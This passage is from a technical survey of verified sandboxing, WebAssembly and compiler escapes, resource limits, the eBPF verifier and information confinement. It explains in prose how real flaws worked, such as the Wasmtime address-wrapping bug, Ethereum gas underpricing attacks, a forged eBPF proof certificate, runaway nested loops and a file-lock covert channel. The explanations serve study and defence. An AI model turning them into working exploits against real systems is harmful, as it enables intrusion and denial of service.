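I(s) ∧ i ∈ L ⇒ no access outside the sandbox succeeds, and either the program stops or I(s′)

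Here s is any processor state and s′ is the state after executing instruction i. If the invariant I holds at the start, it holds after every instruction, however long the program runs and wherever it jumps in its sandbox. The invariant requires x21 to be unchanged, the next instruction to be inside the sandbox, and x18 and the stack pointer to be inside it or within 128 MiB of its edges. The register for return addresses must point into the sandbox or to one of three entry points in LFI's runtime.

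The 128 MiB margin allows for instructions that use the stack pointer and then move it, which can take it just past the edge. LFI leaves the 4 GiB on either side of the sandbox unmapped, meaning those addresses have no memory behind them and any access to them ends the program. The stack pointer can therefore move a few bytes outside the sandbox, but the program can't read or write there.

All ARM64 instructions are 32 bits long, so there are only 4.3 billion. Sotoudeh and Yedidia ran the checker on every one to see which it accepted. For each accepted instruction, their software used a formal specification of ARM64 to work out the instruction's effect on arbitrary register contents, and an automatic solver searched for a state that satisfies the invariant I but leads to a violation. If there is no such state, the instruction is safe. Only the invariant, about 20 lines, is written by hand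 for each sandbox design, whereas RockSalt needed 10,000 lines of proof.

The run took about 20 hours on a 160-core machine for each of LFI's two memory layouts. It found no bugs in the checker but did find errors and omissions in LFI's written specification, including missing guarantees about the memory around the first and last sandboxes. Because the method used the checker's actual verdicts, it avoided RockSalt's gap between the proved version and the C version.

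The theorem assumes that the runtime, which Sotoudeh and Yedidia didn't verify, sets up memory as described and correctly handles the program's requests, such as sending a network packet. Their proof also relies on the solver, their own analysis software and the ARM64 specification, from which they removed some code for atomic instructions (used to coordinate threads) because their tools couldn't process it. ARM doesn't always specify whether a write that straddles unmapped memory and the host's memory stops before or after changing the host's part, so they proved that no harm occurs even if it always stops after.

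The method doesn't carry over directly to x86, where LFI has to treat some sequences of instructions as units and there are too many permitted units to check one by one. Sotoudeh and Yedidia expect that leaving parts of each instruction unspecified, so that one query covers many, would solve this.

### WebAssembly

Google announced in 2017 that it would phase out Native Client in favour of WebAssembly, an instruction set designed for sandboxing. Compilers translate C, C++ or Rust into a WebAssembly module, and the host's runtime checks the module and translates it into machine code. The instruction set leaves out the dangerous operations, so the module needs no masks.

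A module's data is in its linear memory, an array of bytes numbered from zero. Load and store instructions take a position in this array, and an access beyond the end causes a trap, which stops the module. A module can't refer to locations elsewhere in the host's memory, because positions are counted from the start of its own array, wherever the runtime has put it.

Its control flow is just as restricted, with no instruction for jumping to a computed address. A branch can go only to the end of an enclosing block or the start of an enclosing loop, and the runtime keeps return addresses outside linear memory. To call a function chosen at run time, the module gives an index into a table of functions and the type it expects. The runtime traps if the function has a different type.

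Instructions take their inputs from a stack, and a type checker tracks the types of the values on it, much as Java's verifier does. In an example from *Wanilla* (2025), the checker rejects code that pushes the decimal number 3.0 and the whole number 5 and then tries to add them as whole numbers.

WebAssembly's official specification is a mathematical definition, which is unusual for a language in industrial use. Researchers have encoded it in two proof assistants and proved type soundness, treating a trap as a valid way for a program to end rather than as getting stuck. An early version of this work exposed mistakes in the draft specification before it was published. Rao, Radziuk and Watt later extended one of the encodings to the larger WebAssembly 2.0 in *Progressful Interpreters for Efficient WebAssembly Mechanisation* (2025), finding and correcting several errors in the new type system.

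This theorem protects the host from the module, but a bug in the module can still corrupt the module's own data. Linear memory doesn't record where one C variable ends and the next begins, so a buffer overflow in a C program still overwrites neighbouring variables. The overflow can't reach a return address, but under WebAssembly's rules it can change a variable that records whether the user is an administrator. It can also change a stored function-table index, which makes the program call the wrong function of the right type.

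One remedy is MSWasm, a variant of WebAssembly in which a pointer carries the bounds of the object it points to. *AEGIS* (2025) states a type soundness theorem for MSWasm in which reading or writing past those bounds also counts as getting stuck, so the theorem covers overflows inside the sandbox.

### Escapes through the compiler

The soundness proof covers WebAssembly instructions, but the processor runs the machine code that the runtime's compiler produces from them. An error in that compiler can give a harmless module access to the host. This happened in Wasmtime, a widely used runtime whose main compiler is Cranelift.

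Wasmtime normally omits explicit checks on whether an address is in range, to make code run faster. A load instruction adds a 32-bit position to a constant offset, so the result fits in 33 bits. Wasmtime protected the 6 GiB from the start of linear memory, so that any access the compiler was supposed to allow would land in the module's own memory or cause a trap.

GitLab's *CVE-2023-26489* (2023) explains how this went wrong. If a module loads from position 8x, where x is a 32-bit number, WebAssembly requires the product to wrap around at 2³². An x86 processor can multiply by 8 and add the starting address in one instruction, and Cranelift used that instruction to save time. But the processor does the sum with 64-bit numbers, so the product doesn't wrap:

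- correct address: base + (8x mod 2³²)
- address in the compiled code: base + 8x

If x is 2³⁰, then 8x is 2³³, which wraps around to 0, so the module should read the first byte of its own memory. The compiled code instead read a location 8 GiB past the start, beyond the protected range. By choosing x and the offset, a module could read or write anything mapped between about 6 and 34 GiB from its base, including other modules' memory. The bug got a severity score of 9.9 out of 10.

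The fix deleted the faulty translation rules. OSV's *CVE-2023-26489* (2023) lists workarounds for users who couldn't update. These include adding explicit range checks, which slows programs down, and leaving a much larger unmapped area after each memory, which limits how many modules can run at once.

A checker of the finished code, like LFI's, would presumably have rejected the faulty instruction, because a 32-bit number times 8 can point outside the sandbox. Wasmtime had no such checker, so Cranelift was in its trusted base. *TrustMee* (2026), which describes a security system built on Wasmtime, counts two Cranelift bugs on x86 that could have allowed an escape, this one and another from 2021. It lists the compiler among the things the system's users must trust.

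On 9 April 2026, Wasmtime's developers disclosed 12 vulnerabilities, three times as many as in all of 2025. Bytecode Alliance's *Wasmtime's April 9, 2026 Security Advisories* (2026) reports that they found 11 of these in three weeks with tools based on language models. Two were critical and allowed escapes from the sandbox. Neither affected Cranelift on x86, the combination that most production systems have used. Six of the 11 were in Wasmtime's two compilers. Another three were in code that passes text between modules, which a proof about the compilers would not cover.

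One of the critical bugs was in Cranelift's translation for ARM64. According to GitLab's *CVE-2026-34971* (2026), the compiled code computed the same address in two ways, checked one result, and loaded from the other. A module could therefore pass the check with a valid address and read from an invalid one. Positive Technologies' *PT-2026-31688 · Bytecode Alliance · Wasmtime* (2026) adds that this was possible only with 64-bit linear memories and certain protections switched off.

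This bug was in a part of Cranelift that researchers had formally verified. The proof covered an older version of the translation rules, and nobody updated it when version 32 of Wasmtime changed them. After the developers updated the formal model, the verification tool flagged the same bug. The Bytecode Alliance plans to rerun the verification on every change to these rules. The other critical escape was in Winch, Wasmtime's newer compiler, which these proofs don't cover.

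### Verifying the translation

Verification of Cranelift checks one translation rule at a time. A solver compares the original operation with the machine instructions that replace it and looks for an input on which they differ. For the rule behind the 2023 bug, x = 2²⁹ would be such an input. *Lightweight, Modular Verification for WebAssembly-to-Native Instruction Selection* introduced a tool for this. McLoughlin, Sheng and colleagues (2025), in *Scaling Instruction-Selection Verification against Authoritative ISA Semantics*, extended the approach to nearly all the ARM64 rules that Cranelift can apply to programs using only WebAssembly's core features. They found new bugs in Cranelift, and their automation cut the number of handwritten specifications required by a factor of 2.6.

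These proofs cover the choice of instructions but not the rest of the compiler. For example, Cranelift must also assign values to registers, and for that step it relies on a separate checker that its developers test continuously with random programs.

*Isolation Without Taxation* (2021) goes back to checking the finished code. It presents VeriZero, which analyses the x86 output of Lucet, an earlier WebAssembly compiler, and confirms, among other things, that each function restores any registers it was required to preserve and that calls pass the right inputs. This proof makes the sandbox safer and also faster, because the host can call the module directly, without the slow code that would otherwise save and clear registers at every switch between the two.

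A third option is a compiler with a proof for the whole translation. Sotoudeh and Yedidia mention vWasm, a verified compiler from WebAssembly to x86, and WAVE, a verified runtime. But *Extending Lifetime of Embedded Systems by WebAssembly-based Functional Extensions Including Drivers* (2025) observes that industrial runtimes are designed more for performance than for formal correctness, and describes verifying their compilers as an open question.

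### Isolating the parts of one program

A sandbox around a whole program doesn't protect its parts from one another, so a bug in the code that reads images can still corrupt the code that handles passwords. Developers of browsers and other large programs reduce this risk by splitting them into compartments that can interact only through declared functions. In *Blame-aware Recomposition for Secure Compilation Proofs of Low-Level Compartment Isolation*, Schlosser, Thibault and Hrițcu (2026) proved that a compiler preserves this separation down to a machine with ordinary flat memory, where any number can serve as an address. Earlier proofs went only as far as an idealised machine with built-in compartments.

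Let P be the compartments we want to protect, P↓ their compiled form, and C some hostile machine code linked to them. Let m be a finite record of the calls, returns and outputs in one run. The theorem is that whenever C and P↓ together can produce m, there are compartments C′ in the source language and a record m′ such that:

C′ and P together produce m′, and either m ≤ m′ or m′ ≺ m

The first case, m ≤ m′, means that m′ begins with all of m. The second means that m′ matches m up to a point where P itself does something undefined, such as writing past the end of an array. So until P itself does something undefined, hostile machine code can violate only the safety properties of P that a hostile source program could also violate through P's declared functions. A programmer therefore only has to consider attackers who follow the rules of the source language.

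The machine enforces this with tags. Every memory location has a tag naming the compartment that owns it, and a monitor stops the program if one compartment tries to read or write another's data. Return addresses have tags too, and the monitor prevents a compartment from copying a return address or using it twice.

The proof was difficult because compartments can learn about each other in ways that the record m doesn't include. The older proof method replaces C with C′ and needs P to behave exactly as before. But on a flat machine, a compartment could read address 100, which holds part of another compartment's code, and act differently depending on what it finds. Schlosser and colleagues handle this by treating such reads as undefined behaviour in an intermediate version of the machine that exists only for the proof. Compartments compiled from correct source code never make these reads, and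 the proof discards hostile compartments that do.

Memory allocation also leaked information. A compartment could reserve one byte, call another compartment, reserve a second byte and compare the two addresses. A gap between them would show that the other compartment had reserved memory during the call. Schlosser and colleagues changed the allocator to give each compartment its own range of addresses, identified by their leading digits, as in the 1993 segments.

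The proof, checked in Rocq (formerly Coq), is narrower in scope than LFI's in some respects. The source language is a simple relative of C. Its integers are unbounded but the machine's are 32-bit, so the theorem assumes that programs stay within the machine's limits. The theorem doesn't guarantee that a compartment's data stays secret. It also requires a processor that tags every memory location, which ordinary processors don't do. An earlier version of the compiler can target ordinary hardware through software fault isolation, but its developers have only tested that part. Schlosser and colleagues leave proving it to future work because the conditions the proof would have to maintain are much more complex without tags.

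## Limiting processor time and memory use

A program confined to its own memory can still loop forever, or keep requesting memory until the machine has none left. The proofs about types and sandboxes do not rule out endless loops, and no checker can always tell which programs end, because of the halting problem. Engineers can use a language in which every program ends, derive a limit on resource use from a program's text, count steps as the program runs, or refuse to load a program unless a checker can follow it to its end.

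### Languages in which every program ends

In most languages a function may call itself with any argument. Turner (1995), in *Elementary Strong Functional Programming*, proposed a language in which a function may call itself only on a part of the argument it received. For example, a function that adds up the numbers in a tree can call itself on the two branches:

- total(empty tree) = 0
- total(tree with number n and branches a and b) = n + total(a) + total(b)

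Every tree in the language is finite and each call receives a smaller one, so the calls must eventually reach empty trees. This pattern is called structural recursion, and a compiler can enforce it by reading the program's text, without a proof from the programmer. Turner needed two further rules. Every basic operation must return a value, so 0/0 is defined as 0. A data type may not contain functions that take the same type as input, because programmers could use them to build a loop without any visible recursion.

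The rule excludes some familiar algorithms, such as quicksort, which divides a list into smaller and larger numbers and calls itself on both lists. These are new lists, not parts of the old one. Turner replaces quicksort with treesort, which puts the numbers in a tree and works down its branches, making the same comparisons. *Intrinsically Correct Algorithms and Recursive Coalgebras* (2025) notes that simple termination checkers reject most divide-and-conquer algorithms for the same reason. The programmer then has to prove separately that some quantity shrinks with each call. Turner found that about 80% of the algorithms people ordinarily write already fit the rule.

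A language in which every program ends cannot express its own interpreter. Suppose it could, and let u(p, x) be the result of running program p on input x. Then we could write a program d with d(x) = u(x, x) + 1. Running d on its own text would have to give a number equal to itself plus one, which is impossible. *System T of Higher-Order Recursion*, a textbook chapter on a small language of this kind, presents this limit as an unavoidable consequence of making every program end.

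Proof assistants such as Lean restrict recursion to stay sound. In Lean, a proof of a statement is a program whose type is that statement. *WybeCoder* (2026) points out that a function that only called itself could have any type, so it could serve as a proof of a false statement. Loosening the recursion rules is therefore risky, and *Garlene* (Stepanenko and Bahr, 2026) says that such extensions have a well-documented history of making formal systems inconsistent.

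Against an attacker who wants to tie up a machine, though, a guarantee of ending is worth little. The standard example is Ackermann's function:

- if m is 0, A(m, n) = n + 1
- if only n is 0, A(m, n) = A(m − 1, 1)
- if neither is 0, A(m, n) = A(m − 1, A(m, n − 1))

Each call either lowers m, or keeps m the same and lowers n. When m falls, n may become enormous, but it is still finite, so m eventually falls again until it reaches 0. The definition therefore satisfies Turner's full rule, which considers several arguments together. But A(3, n) is 2ⁿ⁺³ − 3, and A(4, 2) is 2⁶⁵⁵³⁶ − 3, a number with 19,729 digits. The equations can raise a number only by adding 1, so a computer that follows them literally needs at least about 2⁶⁵⁵³⁶ steps to compute A(4, 2). More ordinary programs can need impractical amounts of memory. A program that starts with a one-element list and appends the list to itself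 60 times produces more than 10¹⁸ elements.

### Bounds from the program's text

A useful guarantee has to say how much a program will use, preferably as a formula in the size of its input. Hoffmann and Jost (2022), in *Two decades of automatic amortized resource analysis*, survey a method that finds such formulas automatically. It builds on Robert Tarjan's potential method, which assigns each state of a program a number Φ that is never negative. The number works like a prepaid balance, and every step must satisfy:

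Φ(before) ≥ cost of the step + Φ(after)

When we add up these inequalities over a whole run, the intermediate values of Φ cancel. The total resource use is at most Φ(start) − Φ(end), and so at most Φ(start). With Tarjan's method, a person has to invent Φ. Martin Hofmann and Steffen Jost showed in 2003 that a type checker can find it if each element of a list is assigned a fixed amount of potential.

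Take a function append(x, y) that joins two lists. If x is empty, it returns y. Otherwise it splits x into a first element h and the remaining list t, computes z = append(t, y), and returns a new list cell containing h, followed by z. Suppose that creating a cell costs c bytes of memory and everything else is free. Let p, r and s be the unknown amounts of potential on each element of x, y and the result. The program's text gives two conditions:

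- r ≥ s, because the function returns y itself when x is empty, so each element of y must already carry what the result needs.
- p ≥ c + s, because removing h from x releases p units, which must pay for the new cell and for the potential on it.

The recursive call adds no condition, since the elements of t and y carry the potential it requires. If nothing else will use the result, we can set s = 0, and the smallest solution is r = 0 and p = c. For lists of lengths n and m, the starting potential is then cn + 0m, so append uses at most cn bytes. The length of the second list doesn't affect the bound, because append never copies that list.

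The variable s makes the analysis work for larger programs. In append(append(x, y), z), the outer call copies every element of the inner result, so the inner result must have s = c. The two conditions then give r = c and p = 2c, for a total of c(2n + m), which is correct because the program copies x twice and y once. All the conditions are linear inequalities, which standard software can solve automatically.

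The same proof covers stack space or processor time if each operation is assigned the amount of that resource it uses. Those amounts must match the real machine. Hoffmann and Jost report that combining this method with separate bounds for short stretches of machine code gave a time bound less than 34% above the slowest measured run on a simple processor, the Renesas M32C/85.

The method looks only for formulas of certain shapes, so it can fail on a program that does have a bound. It also has to prevent a program from using the same potential twice. If a program makes two references to a list, the type checker divides the potential between them, but this is awkward for functions that store earlier arguments. For example, a program may give append its first list, x, and supply the second later. The first call requires no potential and returns a function that stores x. Each call to that function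 requires c units of potential for each element of x. Earlier systems had to fix in advance how many times the program could call the returned function. *Dependently-Typed AARA* (Xu and Wang, 2026) separates the potential from the data, so the type of append can specify that the first call requires no potential and each later call requires potential proportional to the length of x.

Compilation can invalidate a bound on the source program. *A formally verified compiler back-end* (2009), which describes the verified C compiler CompCert, explains that a compiler may move variables onto the stack when it runs out of registers. The compiled program can then need more stack space than its source suggests. Carbonneaux, Hoffmann and colleagues (2014), in *End-to-End Verification of Stack-Space Bounds for C Programs*, handle this by leaving the sizes open. If f calls g and later h, the stack must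 hold f's data plus whichever of the other two needs more:

S(f) = M(f) + max(S(g), S(h))

Here S is the total stack space a call needs and M is the space for the function's own data. The compiler supplies the values of M, and a machine-checked proof guarantees that the resulting bound is enough for the compiled program. The analysis is automatic only for functions that don't call themselves, and a person has to prove the bound for those that do. Carbonneaux and colleagues used the analysis on the entire CertiKOS operating-system kernel. *Verifying Device Drivers with Pancake* (2025) gives a similar guarantee for a language for device drivers.

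A crude rule is sometimes enough to limit the memory that a program requests as it runs. Barthe mentions a verified checker that accepts a program written in JavaCard, the version of Java for smart cards, only if the program never allocates memory inside a loop.

### Gas and fuel

Metering deducts units from a budget for each step a program takes and stops the program when the budget runs out. If every step uses at least one unit, a budget of G units allows at most G steps, whatever the program. Turner used much the same idea to fit awkward algorithms into a language where every program ends. The programmer adds an argument that starts at an upper limit on the number of steps and decreases with each call.

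A limit on steps is not yet a limit on seconds. Suppose instruction i has price gᵢ and takes time tᵢ on a real machine. Then the most that a budget of G units can buy is:

total time ≤ G × max(tᵢ/gᵢ)

An attacker will therefore fill a program with whichever instruction takes the most time for its price. This happened to Ethereum, a blockchain on which thousands of computers each execute every smart contract. Whoever sends a transaction limits how many units, called gas, it can use, and pays for those it does use. If the gas runs out, the computers undo the contract's changes, but the sender still pays.

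In September 2016, attackers began sending transactions that repeatedly used EXTCODESIZE, an instruction that looks up the size of another contract's code. Each lookup cost 20 gas, less than seven additions, but often required a computer to read from its disk. The attackers fit about 50,000 lookups into each block, or batch of transactions, for only about a million gas. Computers took 20 to 60 seconds to process such a block, while new blocks normally arrived about every 15 seconds. Another attack used a free instruction for deleting contracts to create about 19 million empty accounts, which every computer then had to store.

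In October, Ethereum's developers raised the price of deleting a contract to 5,000 gas and the price of EXTCODESIZE to 700, so a million gas bought about 1,400 lookups instead of 50,000. In November they introduced rules for clearing away the empty accounts. They raised the price of lookups again in 2021, to 2,600 gas for the first lookup of each account in a transaction, because the database had grown and reading it took longer. The limit on steps worked throughout these attacks, and no transaction used more gas than its sender had bought. The error was in the prices, which rest on empirical assumptions about hardware that go out of date.

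Metering also leaves users unsure how much gas to buy. Hoffmann and Jost note that a sender usually has to commit to a gas payment without knowing what is in the contract's memory, and they suggest using the potential method to predict the cost. With a bound like the one for append, the sender would at least know which list determines the price.

WebAssembly runtimes offer the same mechanism, called fuel. In Wasmtime, the host gives a module some fuel, most instructions use one unit, and the module traps when it has none left. A few instructions use no fuel, such as the one that marks the start of a loop, but a module still can't run forever without using any, because repeating the loop requires a branch, which uses one unit. WebAssembly also has instructions that fill or copy a whole block of memory. If each of these used one unit, filling a gigabyte would use as much fuel as adding two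 numbers, so to limit real time, a host has to deduct fuel for them according to the size of the block. It also has to deduct fuel for work it does at the module's request, because counting the module's own instructions misses that work.

Counting fuel slows programs down. Wasmtime has a faster alternative in which a timer periodically advances a counter, and the compiled code checks the counter at the start of each function and each pass through a loop. This limits real time more directly, but two runs of the same program may stop at different places. A blockchain can't use this method because all its computers have to agree on the result.

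### The eBPF verifier

Linux lets administrators load small programs into its kernel, for instance to filter network traffic or record what the machine is doing. These programs use an instruction set called eBPF and share the kernel's memory, and one that never ends can freeze the machine. Before running a program, the kernel therefore uses a component called the eBPF verifier to try to prove that the program accesses only permitted memory and ends on every input.

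The verifier follows each path through the program without using actual values. For every register, it records a range of possible values and which individual bits must be 0 or 1. After a test such as "if n is negative, stop", it continues with a range for n that starts at 0. Twenty yes-or-no tests in a row give more than a million paths, so the verifier abandons a path if it reaches an instruction it has already checked for a wider set of values. It rejects the program if it has to examine more than a million instructions over all paths combined. The limit was 131,072 until 2019. Programmers sometimes have to break up large programs to stay below the limit.

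*Keel* (Cai, Chang and Nagarakatte, 2026) gives an example of a safe program that the verifier rejects. The program writes two records into an 800-byte buffer. The first takes u bytes, where u is between 0 and 800. The second starts at position u and takes up to 800 − u bytes, so it can't extend past byte 800. But the verifier stores the starting position and the length as two separate ranges, each from 0 to 800. It adds them, calculates that the write might reach byte 1,600, and rejects the program.

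The verifier has also accepted dangerous programs. *Kernel extension verification is untenable* (Jia, Sahu and colleagues, 2023) counts at least 22 verifier bugs that developers fixed in 2021 and 2022. One of these, a missing check on pointers, let ordinary users read and write any kernel memory and take control of the machine. The verifier's routine tests now include Agni, a tool that translates the range-tracking code into logic and checks it with a solver. Range tracking still causes problems. *Detecting Empty Abstractions and Pruning Dead Paths in the Linux eBPF Verifier* (2026) cites a warning from a test version of Linux 6.19, in which the verifier's sanity check found that a register's bounds had broken the verifier's rules.

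Jia and colleagues think even a perfect verifier would not be enough, because eBPF programs call helper functions, ordinary kernel code that the verifier doesn't examine. Linux 5.18 had 249 of them, and about a third could end up calling 500 or more other kernel functions. Developers fixed at least 18 security-related bugs in the helpers in the same two years. Jia and colleagues found another, which let an approved program crash the kernel.

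They also made the guarantee that programs end useless in practice. A helper called bpf_loop repeats a function up to about 8.4 million times, and that function can itself call bpf_loop. As with Ackermann's function, every loop has a limit, but nesting multiplies the limits, so three levels allow about 6 × 10²⁰ repetitions, which would take almost 19,000 years at a billion per second. Jia and colleagues ran a program of this kind for 800 seconds while it held a lock that other parts of the kernel needed, and calculated that they could make one run for millions of years.

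### Proofs and run-time checks for kernel extensions

One response to the wrongly rejected programs is to let someone else supply the missing proof. In 2025, researchers presented the eBPF Certificate Framework (BCF), which Cai and colleagues describe. When the verifier can't establish a safety condition C on a path where condition P holds, it constructs the formula "P and not C". A solver outside the kernel then tries to prove that no values satisfy this formula. In the example with two records, the formula is:

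0 ≤ u ≤ 800 and u + (800 − u) > 800

The left side of the second inequality is always 800, so the formula is contradictory and the write is safe. The solver's proof has 33 steps and takes up 852 bytes. The kernel checks each step itself, so it doesn't have to trust the solver. In a second project, Proof-Carrying BPF, the compiler generates the proofs in advance.

This puts the proof checker in the kernel's trusted base, and BCF's checker was about 5,000 lines of unverified C. Cai and colleagues found 13 bugs in it when they tried to formalise it. The checker accepted some kinds of proof step without checking them. One of its rules simplified a comparison between two products, y × a < x × a, in a way that works for ordinary whole numbers but not for numbers that wrap around. With 8-bit numbers, 64 × 2 wraps around to −128, so for y = 64, x = 0 and a = 2 the original comparison is true and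 the simplified one is false. The rule treats the two as equivalent, and Cai and colleagues used that error to build a 13-step "proof" that BCF's checker accepted for any condition. An attacker could use such a forgery to get an unsafe program past a safety check.

Keel, a replacement for BCF's checker, comes with a machine-checked proof that it accepts only valid certificates. In tests it loaded the same 1,226 of 1,588 program files as BCF's checker, and it rejected the forged certificates. The verifier still constructs the formulas, so a mistake in them could let a dangerous program load.

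Keel also has to protect itself, because an attacker could submit a small certificate that takes an enormous time to check. It does so by metering its own work. Before reading a certificate, it sets one budget for time and one for memory, both proportional to the size of the input. It deducts from them before every loop, search or allocation whose cost depends on the input, and rejects the certificate if a budget is too low. Cai and colleagues treat what remains of the budget as the potential in Tarjan's method, and prove:

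T ≤ R × W

Here T is the number of steps in their model of C, W is the initial time budget, and R is a constant, the maximum number of steps per unit of budget.

The counters make this proof much easier than a direct analysis. Keel stores terms in a hash table, which is fast unless many items are assigned the same position, and an attacker could choose items that are. A direct analysis would have to prove a limit on these collisions. With the counters, each extra search uses one unit of the budget, so the bound holds even if every item collides. Removing the counters speeds up processing of the ten largest certificates by only 2%, and no genuine certificate in the tests ran out of budget. The theorem bounds the number of steps in a model, so the limit in seconds depends on how long the slowest of those steps takes on a real processor.

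Better proofs don't solve the problems with helper functions. Jia and colleagues propose dropping the verifier and writing extensions in Rust without unsafe blocks. A trusted compiler outside the kernel would check and sign each extension, and the kernel would check only the signature. Since Rust is more expressive than eBPF, programmers would need fewer helpers. Rust doesn't guarantee that a program ends, so a timer would stop any extension that ran too long.

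Stopping an extension cleanly is difficult. If it holds a lock when the timer expires, something has to release it. Ordinary Rust programs do this by running clean-up code for each object, but here an untrusted author may have written that code, and the usual clean-up mechanism needs to allocate memory when the kernel may be unable to. *Rex* (Jia, Qin and colleagues, 2025) describes a later system for Rust extensions that combines the language's checks with run-time protection. Cai and colleagues object that approaches like this enlarge the trusted base, since the kernel then relies on Rust's runtime.

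Two other projects stay closer to eBPF. *BeePL* (Priya, 2025) presents a language whose type system provably guarantees that programs end and use memory safely, along with a verified compiler to eBPF. *Kops* (2026) lets developers add new operations without changing the verifier's analysis. Each operation comes with an equivalent sequence of eBPF instructions, which the verifier checks each time a program loads. For seven such operations, proofs in Lean show that the fast version has the same effect as its eBPF sequence.

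### Operating-system quotas

Ordinary programs outside the kernel don't need any of this, because a hardware timer interrupts them many times a second and returns control to the operating system, which can suspend or end them. Linux can, for example, limit a group of processes to 20 milliseconds of processor time in every 100 and to a gigabyte of memory. Such quotas work on any program in any language. They measure actual time and memory, so an attacker gains nothing from an instruction whose assigned weight understates what it uses. They are usually the sensible choice for an untrusted program that can have its own process.

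Quotas rely on the kernel being able to interrupt the program, which makes them a poor fit for eBPF. Code inside the kernel may hold a lock or run at a moment when the kernel can't safely suspend it. Quotas also act only after a program has used up its allowance, and may end it halfway through updating a file. With a proved bound, the operator knows beforehand the most time or memory the program can use, and can reject the job or reserve enough capacity to finish it.

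Limiting what one program uses does not guarantee that another gets what it needs. Aircraft control software, for example, must get enough processor time whenever it has to act. In *formal verification +- resource exhaustion*, a post to a cryptography mailing list, Metzger (2017) argues that engineers can specify and verify limits on memory and stack like any other property, but says it is still quite hard to prove that a program will get enough processor time.

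### Attacks within the budget

None of these limits restricts the number of programs or requests. If each request may use G units and an attacker sends N of them, the total can reach N × G. If a server allows 10 milliseconds of processor time per request, 100 requests a second that each use the full allowance will occupy one processor completely without exceeding the limit. The same applies to memory if the server handles many requests at once.

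The usual defence is a further quota for each user, but an attacker may control thousands of accounts or computers. If many users share one quota, the attacker can use it up and lock the others out. Ethereum charges money for gas, so flooding the network costs more the longer it lasts. Charging deters attackers only if an attack costs more than they hope to gain, and it makes the system more expensive for everyone else.

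A budget can also stop work that ought to finish. In 2016 an Ethereum contract called GovernMental owed one player a jackpot of about 1,100 ether, Ethereum's currency. Before paying, it had to clear its list of participants. The list had grown so long that clearing it took more gas than the network then allowed in one transaction, so every attempt to pay ran out of gas and had no effect. Nobody had attacked the contract, but anyone who can add entries to a list that a metered program must process in one go can block the program in the same way. To rule that out, developers have to prove that the program's resource use stays below the limit for every list it can accumulate, or make it process the list in pieces.

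## Controlling what a program can communicate

A program can stay inside its memory region and its budget and still leak the data it works on. Lampson (1973), in *A Note on the Confinement Problem*, considered a customer who runs someone else's program on confidential data. Suppose the program is a tax calculator written by a stranger. If it gets the tax wrong, the customer has the wrong answer as evidence, but there is usually no sign if it secretly sends the customer's income to its author. The confinement problem is how to run such a program so that it can't pass information to anyone except the customer.

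### Storage, legitimate and covert channels

Lampson sorted the ways a program can leak data into three kinds. One kind, storage channels, uses storage maintained by the operating system that the program can write and an outsider can read. For example, a calculator program could write data to a file in its author's folder. It could also use file locks, if the system never lets anyone write to a file while someone else is reading it. The calculator opens a file for reading to signal a 1 and closes it to signal a 0. The author's program tries to open the same file for writing, and a refusal means 1. The two programs use two more files to signal when a bit is ready and when it has arrived. The calculator needs only permission to read files that its author can write. The operating system can close this channel by giving the reader a private copy whenever someone else tries to write, so that the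 attempt always succeeds.

Legitimate channels are outputs the program is supposed to have. If the calculator charges for its work, its author has to get a copy of the bill, and the last few digits of the price can encode data.

Covert channels send information through something that isn't meant for communication. The calculator could alternate between heavy computation and disk access, and another program on the same machine would detect the change in speed.

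Forbidding the calculator to call any other program would confine it, but even reading a file involves a call to the operating system. Lampson therefore allowed calls to programs that are confined or trusted not to leak. The customer should decide what information goes out through the bill and the system load. The customer could compute the bill from a published price formula, and the operating system could slow the program down or add pointless disk accesses until its behaviour matches what the customer specified. Where that is too inefficient, Lampson suggested limiting how fast information can leak through the channel.

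This approach requires someone to list every channel before blocking it, but Lampson doubted that there was any rigorous way to make such a list for even a moderately complex system.

### Capabilities

Many leaks are possible only because programs have far more access than they need. Miller and Shapiro, in *Paradigm Regained*, compare two Unix commands that both copy a file:

```
cp foo.txt bar.txt
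cat < foo.txt > bar.txt
```

The first command gives the program `cp` two file names. `cp` must be able to open any file its user might name, so it runs with all of the user's rights. In the second command, the user's shell opens both files and passes the open files to `cat`. `cat` needs no other access to do its job, although ordinary systems still give it all the user's rights.

An open file handed over like this is close to a capability, an unforgeable reference that names a resource and grants the right to use it. In a pure capability system, programs have no other way to affect anything. A program can hold a reference only if it started with it, created the object itself, or received the reference in a message from another program that already had it. Miller and Shapiro summarize this as "only connectivity begets connectivity". A program that has no reference to the network, and can't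 reach another program that would give it one, can't make network requests, so the system doesn't need to check for them.

This works only if programs can't forge references. Type-checked languages guarantee that, but Miller and Shapiro still exclude Java from the model because any two Java objects can communicate through shared global variables. A WebAssembly module comes closer because it can call only the outside functions its host supplies. CHERI, an extension to processor designs, builds capabilities into the hardware. Barthe reports machine-checked proofs that a program running on CHERI can never increase the rights its capabilities carry.

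A capability gives full and permanent access, which is often too much, but a wrapper can limit it. Suppose a program should fetch weather forecasts and do nothing else online. The host creates an object that holds the network reference, accepts a city's name, checks it against a list, and requests that city's forecast. The program gets a reference to this object instead of the network. A wrapper can also have an off switch that lets the host withdraw access later.

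The wrapper's code is now in the trusted base. Swasey, Garg and Dreyer (2017), in *Robust and Compositional Verification of Object Capability Patterns*, proved in Coq that the guarantees of several common wrappers hold against arbitrary untrusted code. Their simplest example is a read-only wrapper around a memory cell. The owner keeps the cell and gives untrusted code a function that returns its contents. The proof requires that the contents never include a way to reach the owner's private data, because untrusted code can use whatever it reads. If the cell starts with 2 and its owner never changes it, it will always contain 2, whatever untrusted code does with the wrapper.

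Critics long held that capability systems can't enforce confinement, a view that *Capability Myths Demolished* (Miller, Yee and Shapiro, 2003) calls a myth. The objection goes back to W. E. Boebert in 1984. Suppose a program with low clearance may send data to one with high clearance, but nothing may flow back. The low program could send the high program a capability to write to one of the low program's files, and the high program could use it to send secrets down. Miller and Shapiro reply with a wrapper that passes only whole numbers, so no capability can get through.

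The analysis leaves out covert channels, but the permitted channel can also leak secrets. If the weather wrapper's list has 1,024 cities, the program's choice of city can convey 10 bits of a secret with every request, even though the wrapper is meant to allow these requests.

### Noninterference

To rule out leaks without listing channels, we need a definition of what it means for nothing to leak. Goguen and Meseguer (1982), in *Security Policies and Security Models*, gave one that most later work builds on. They model a system as a machine that receives commands from several users. Let w be a sequence of commands, each labelled with the user who gave it, and let out(w, u) be what user u sees after the machine has carried out w. For a group of users G, let purge(w, G) be the same sequence with every command from G deleted. Then G does not interfere with another group G′ if:

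∀w, ∀u ∈ G′: out(w, u) = out(purge(w, G), u)

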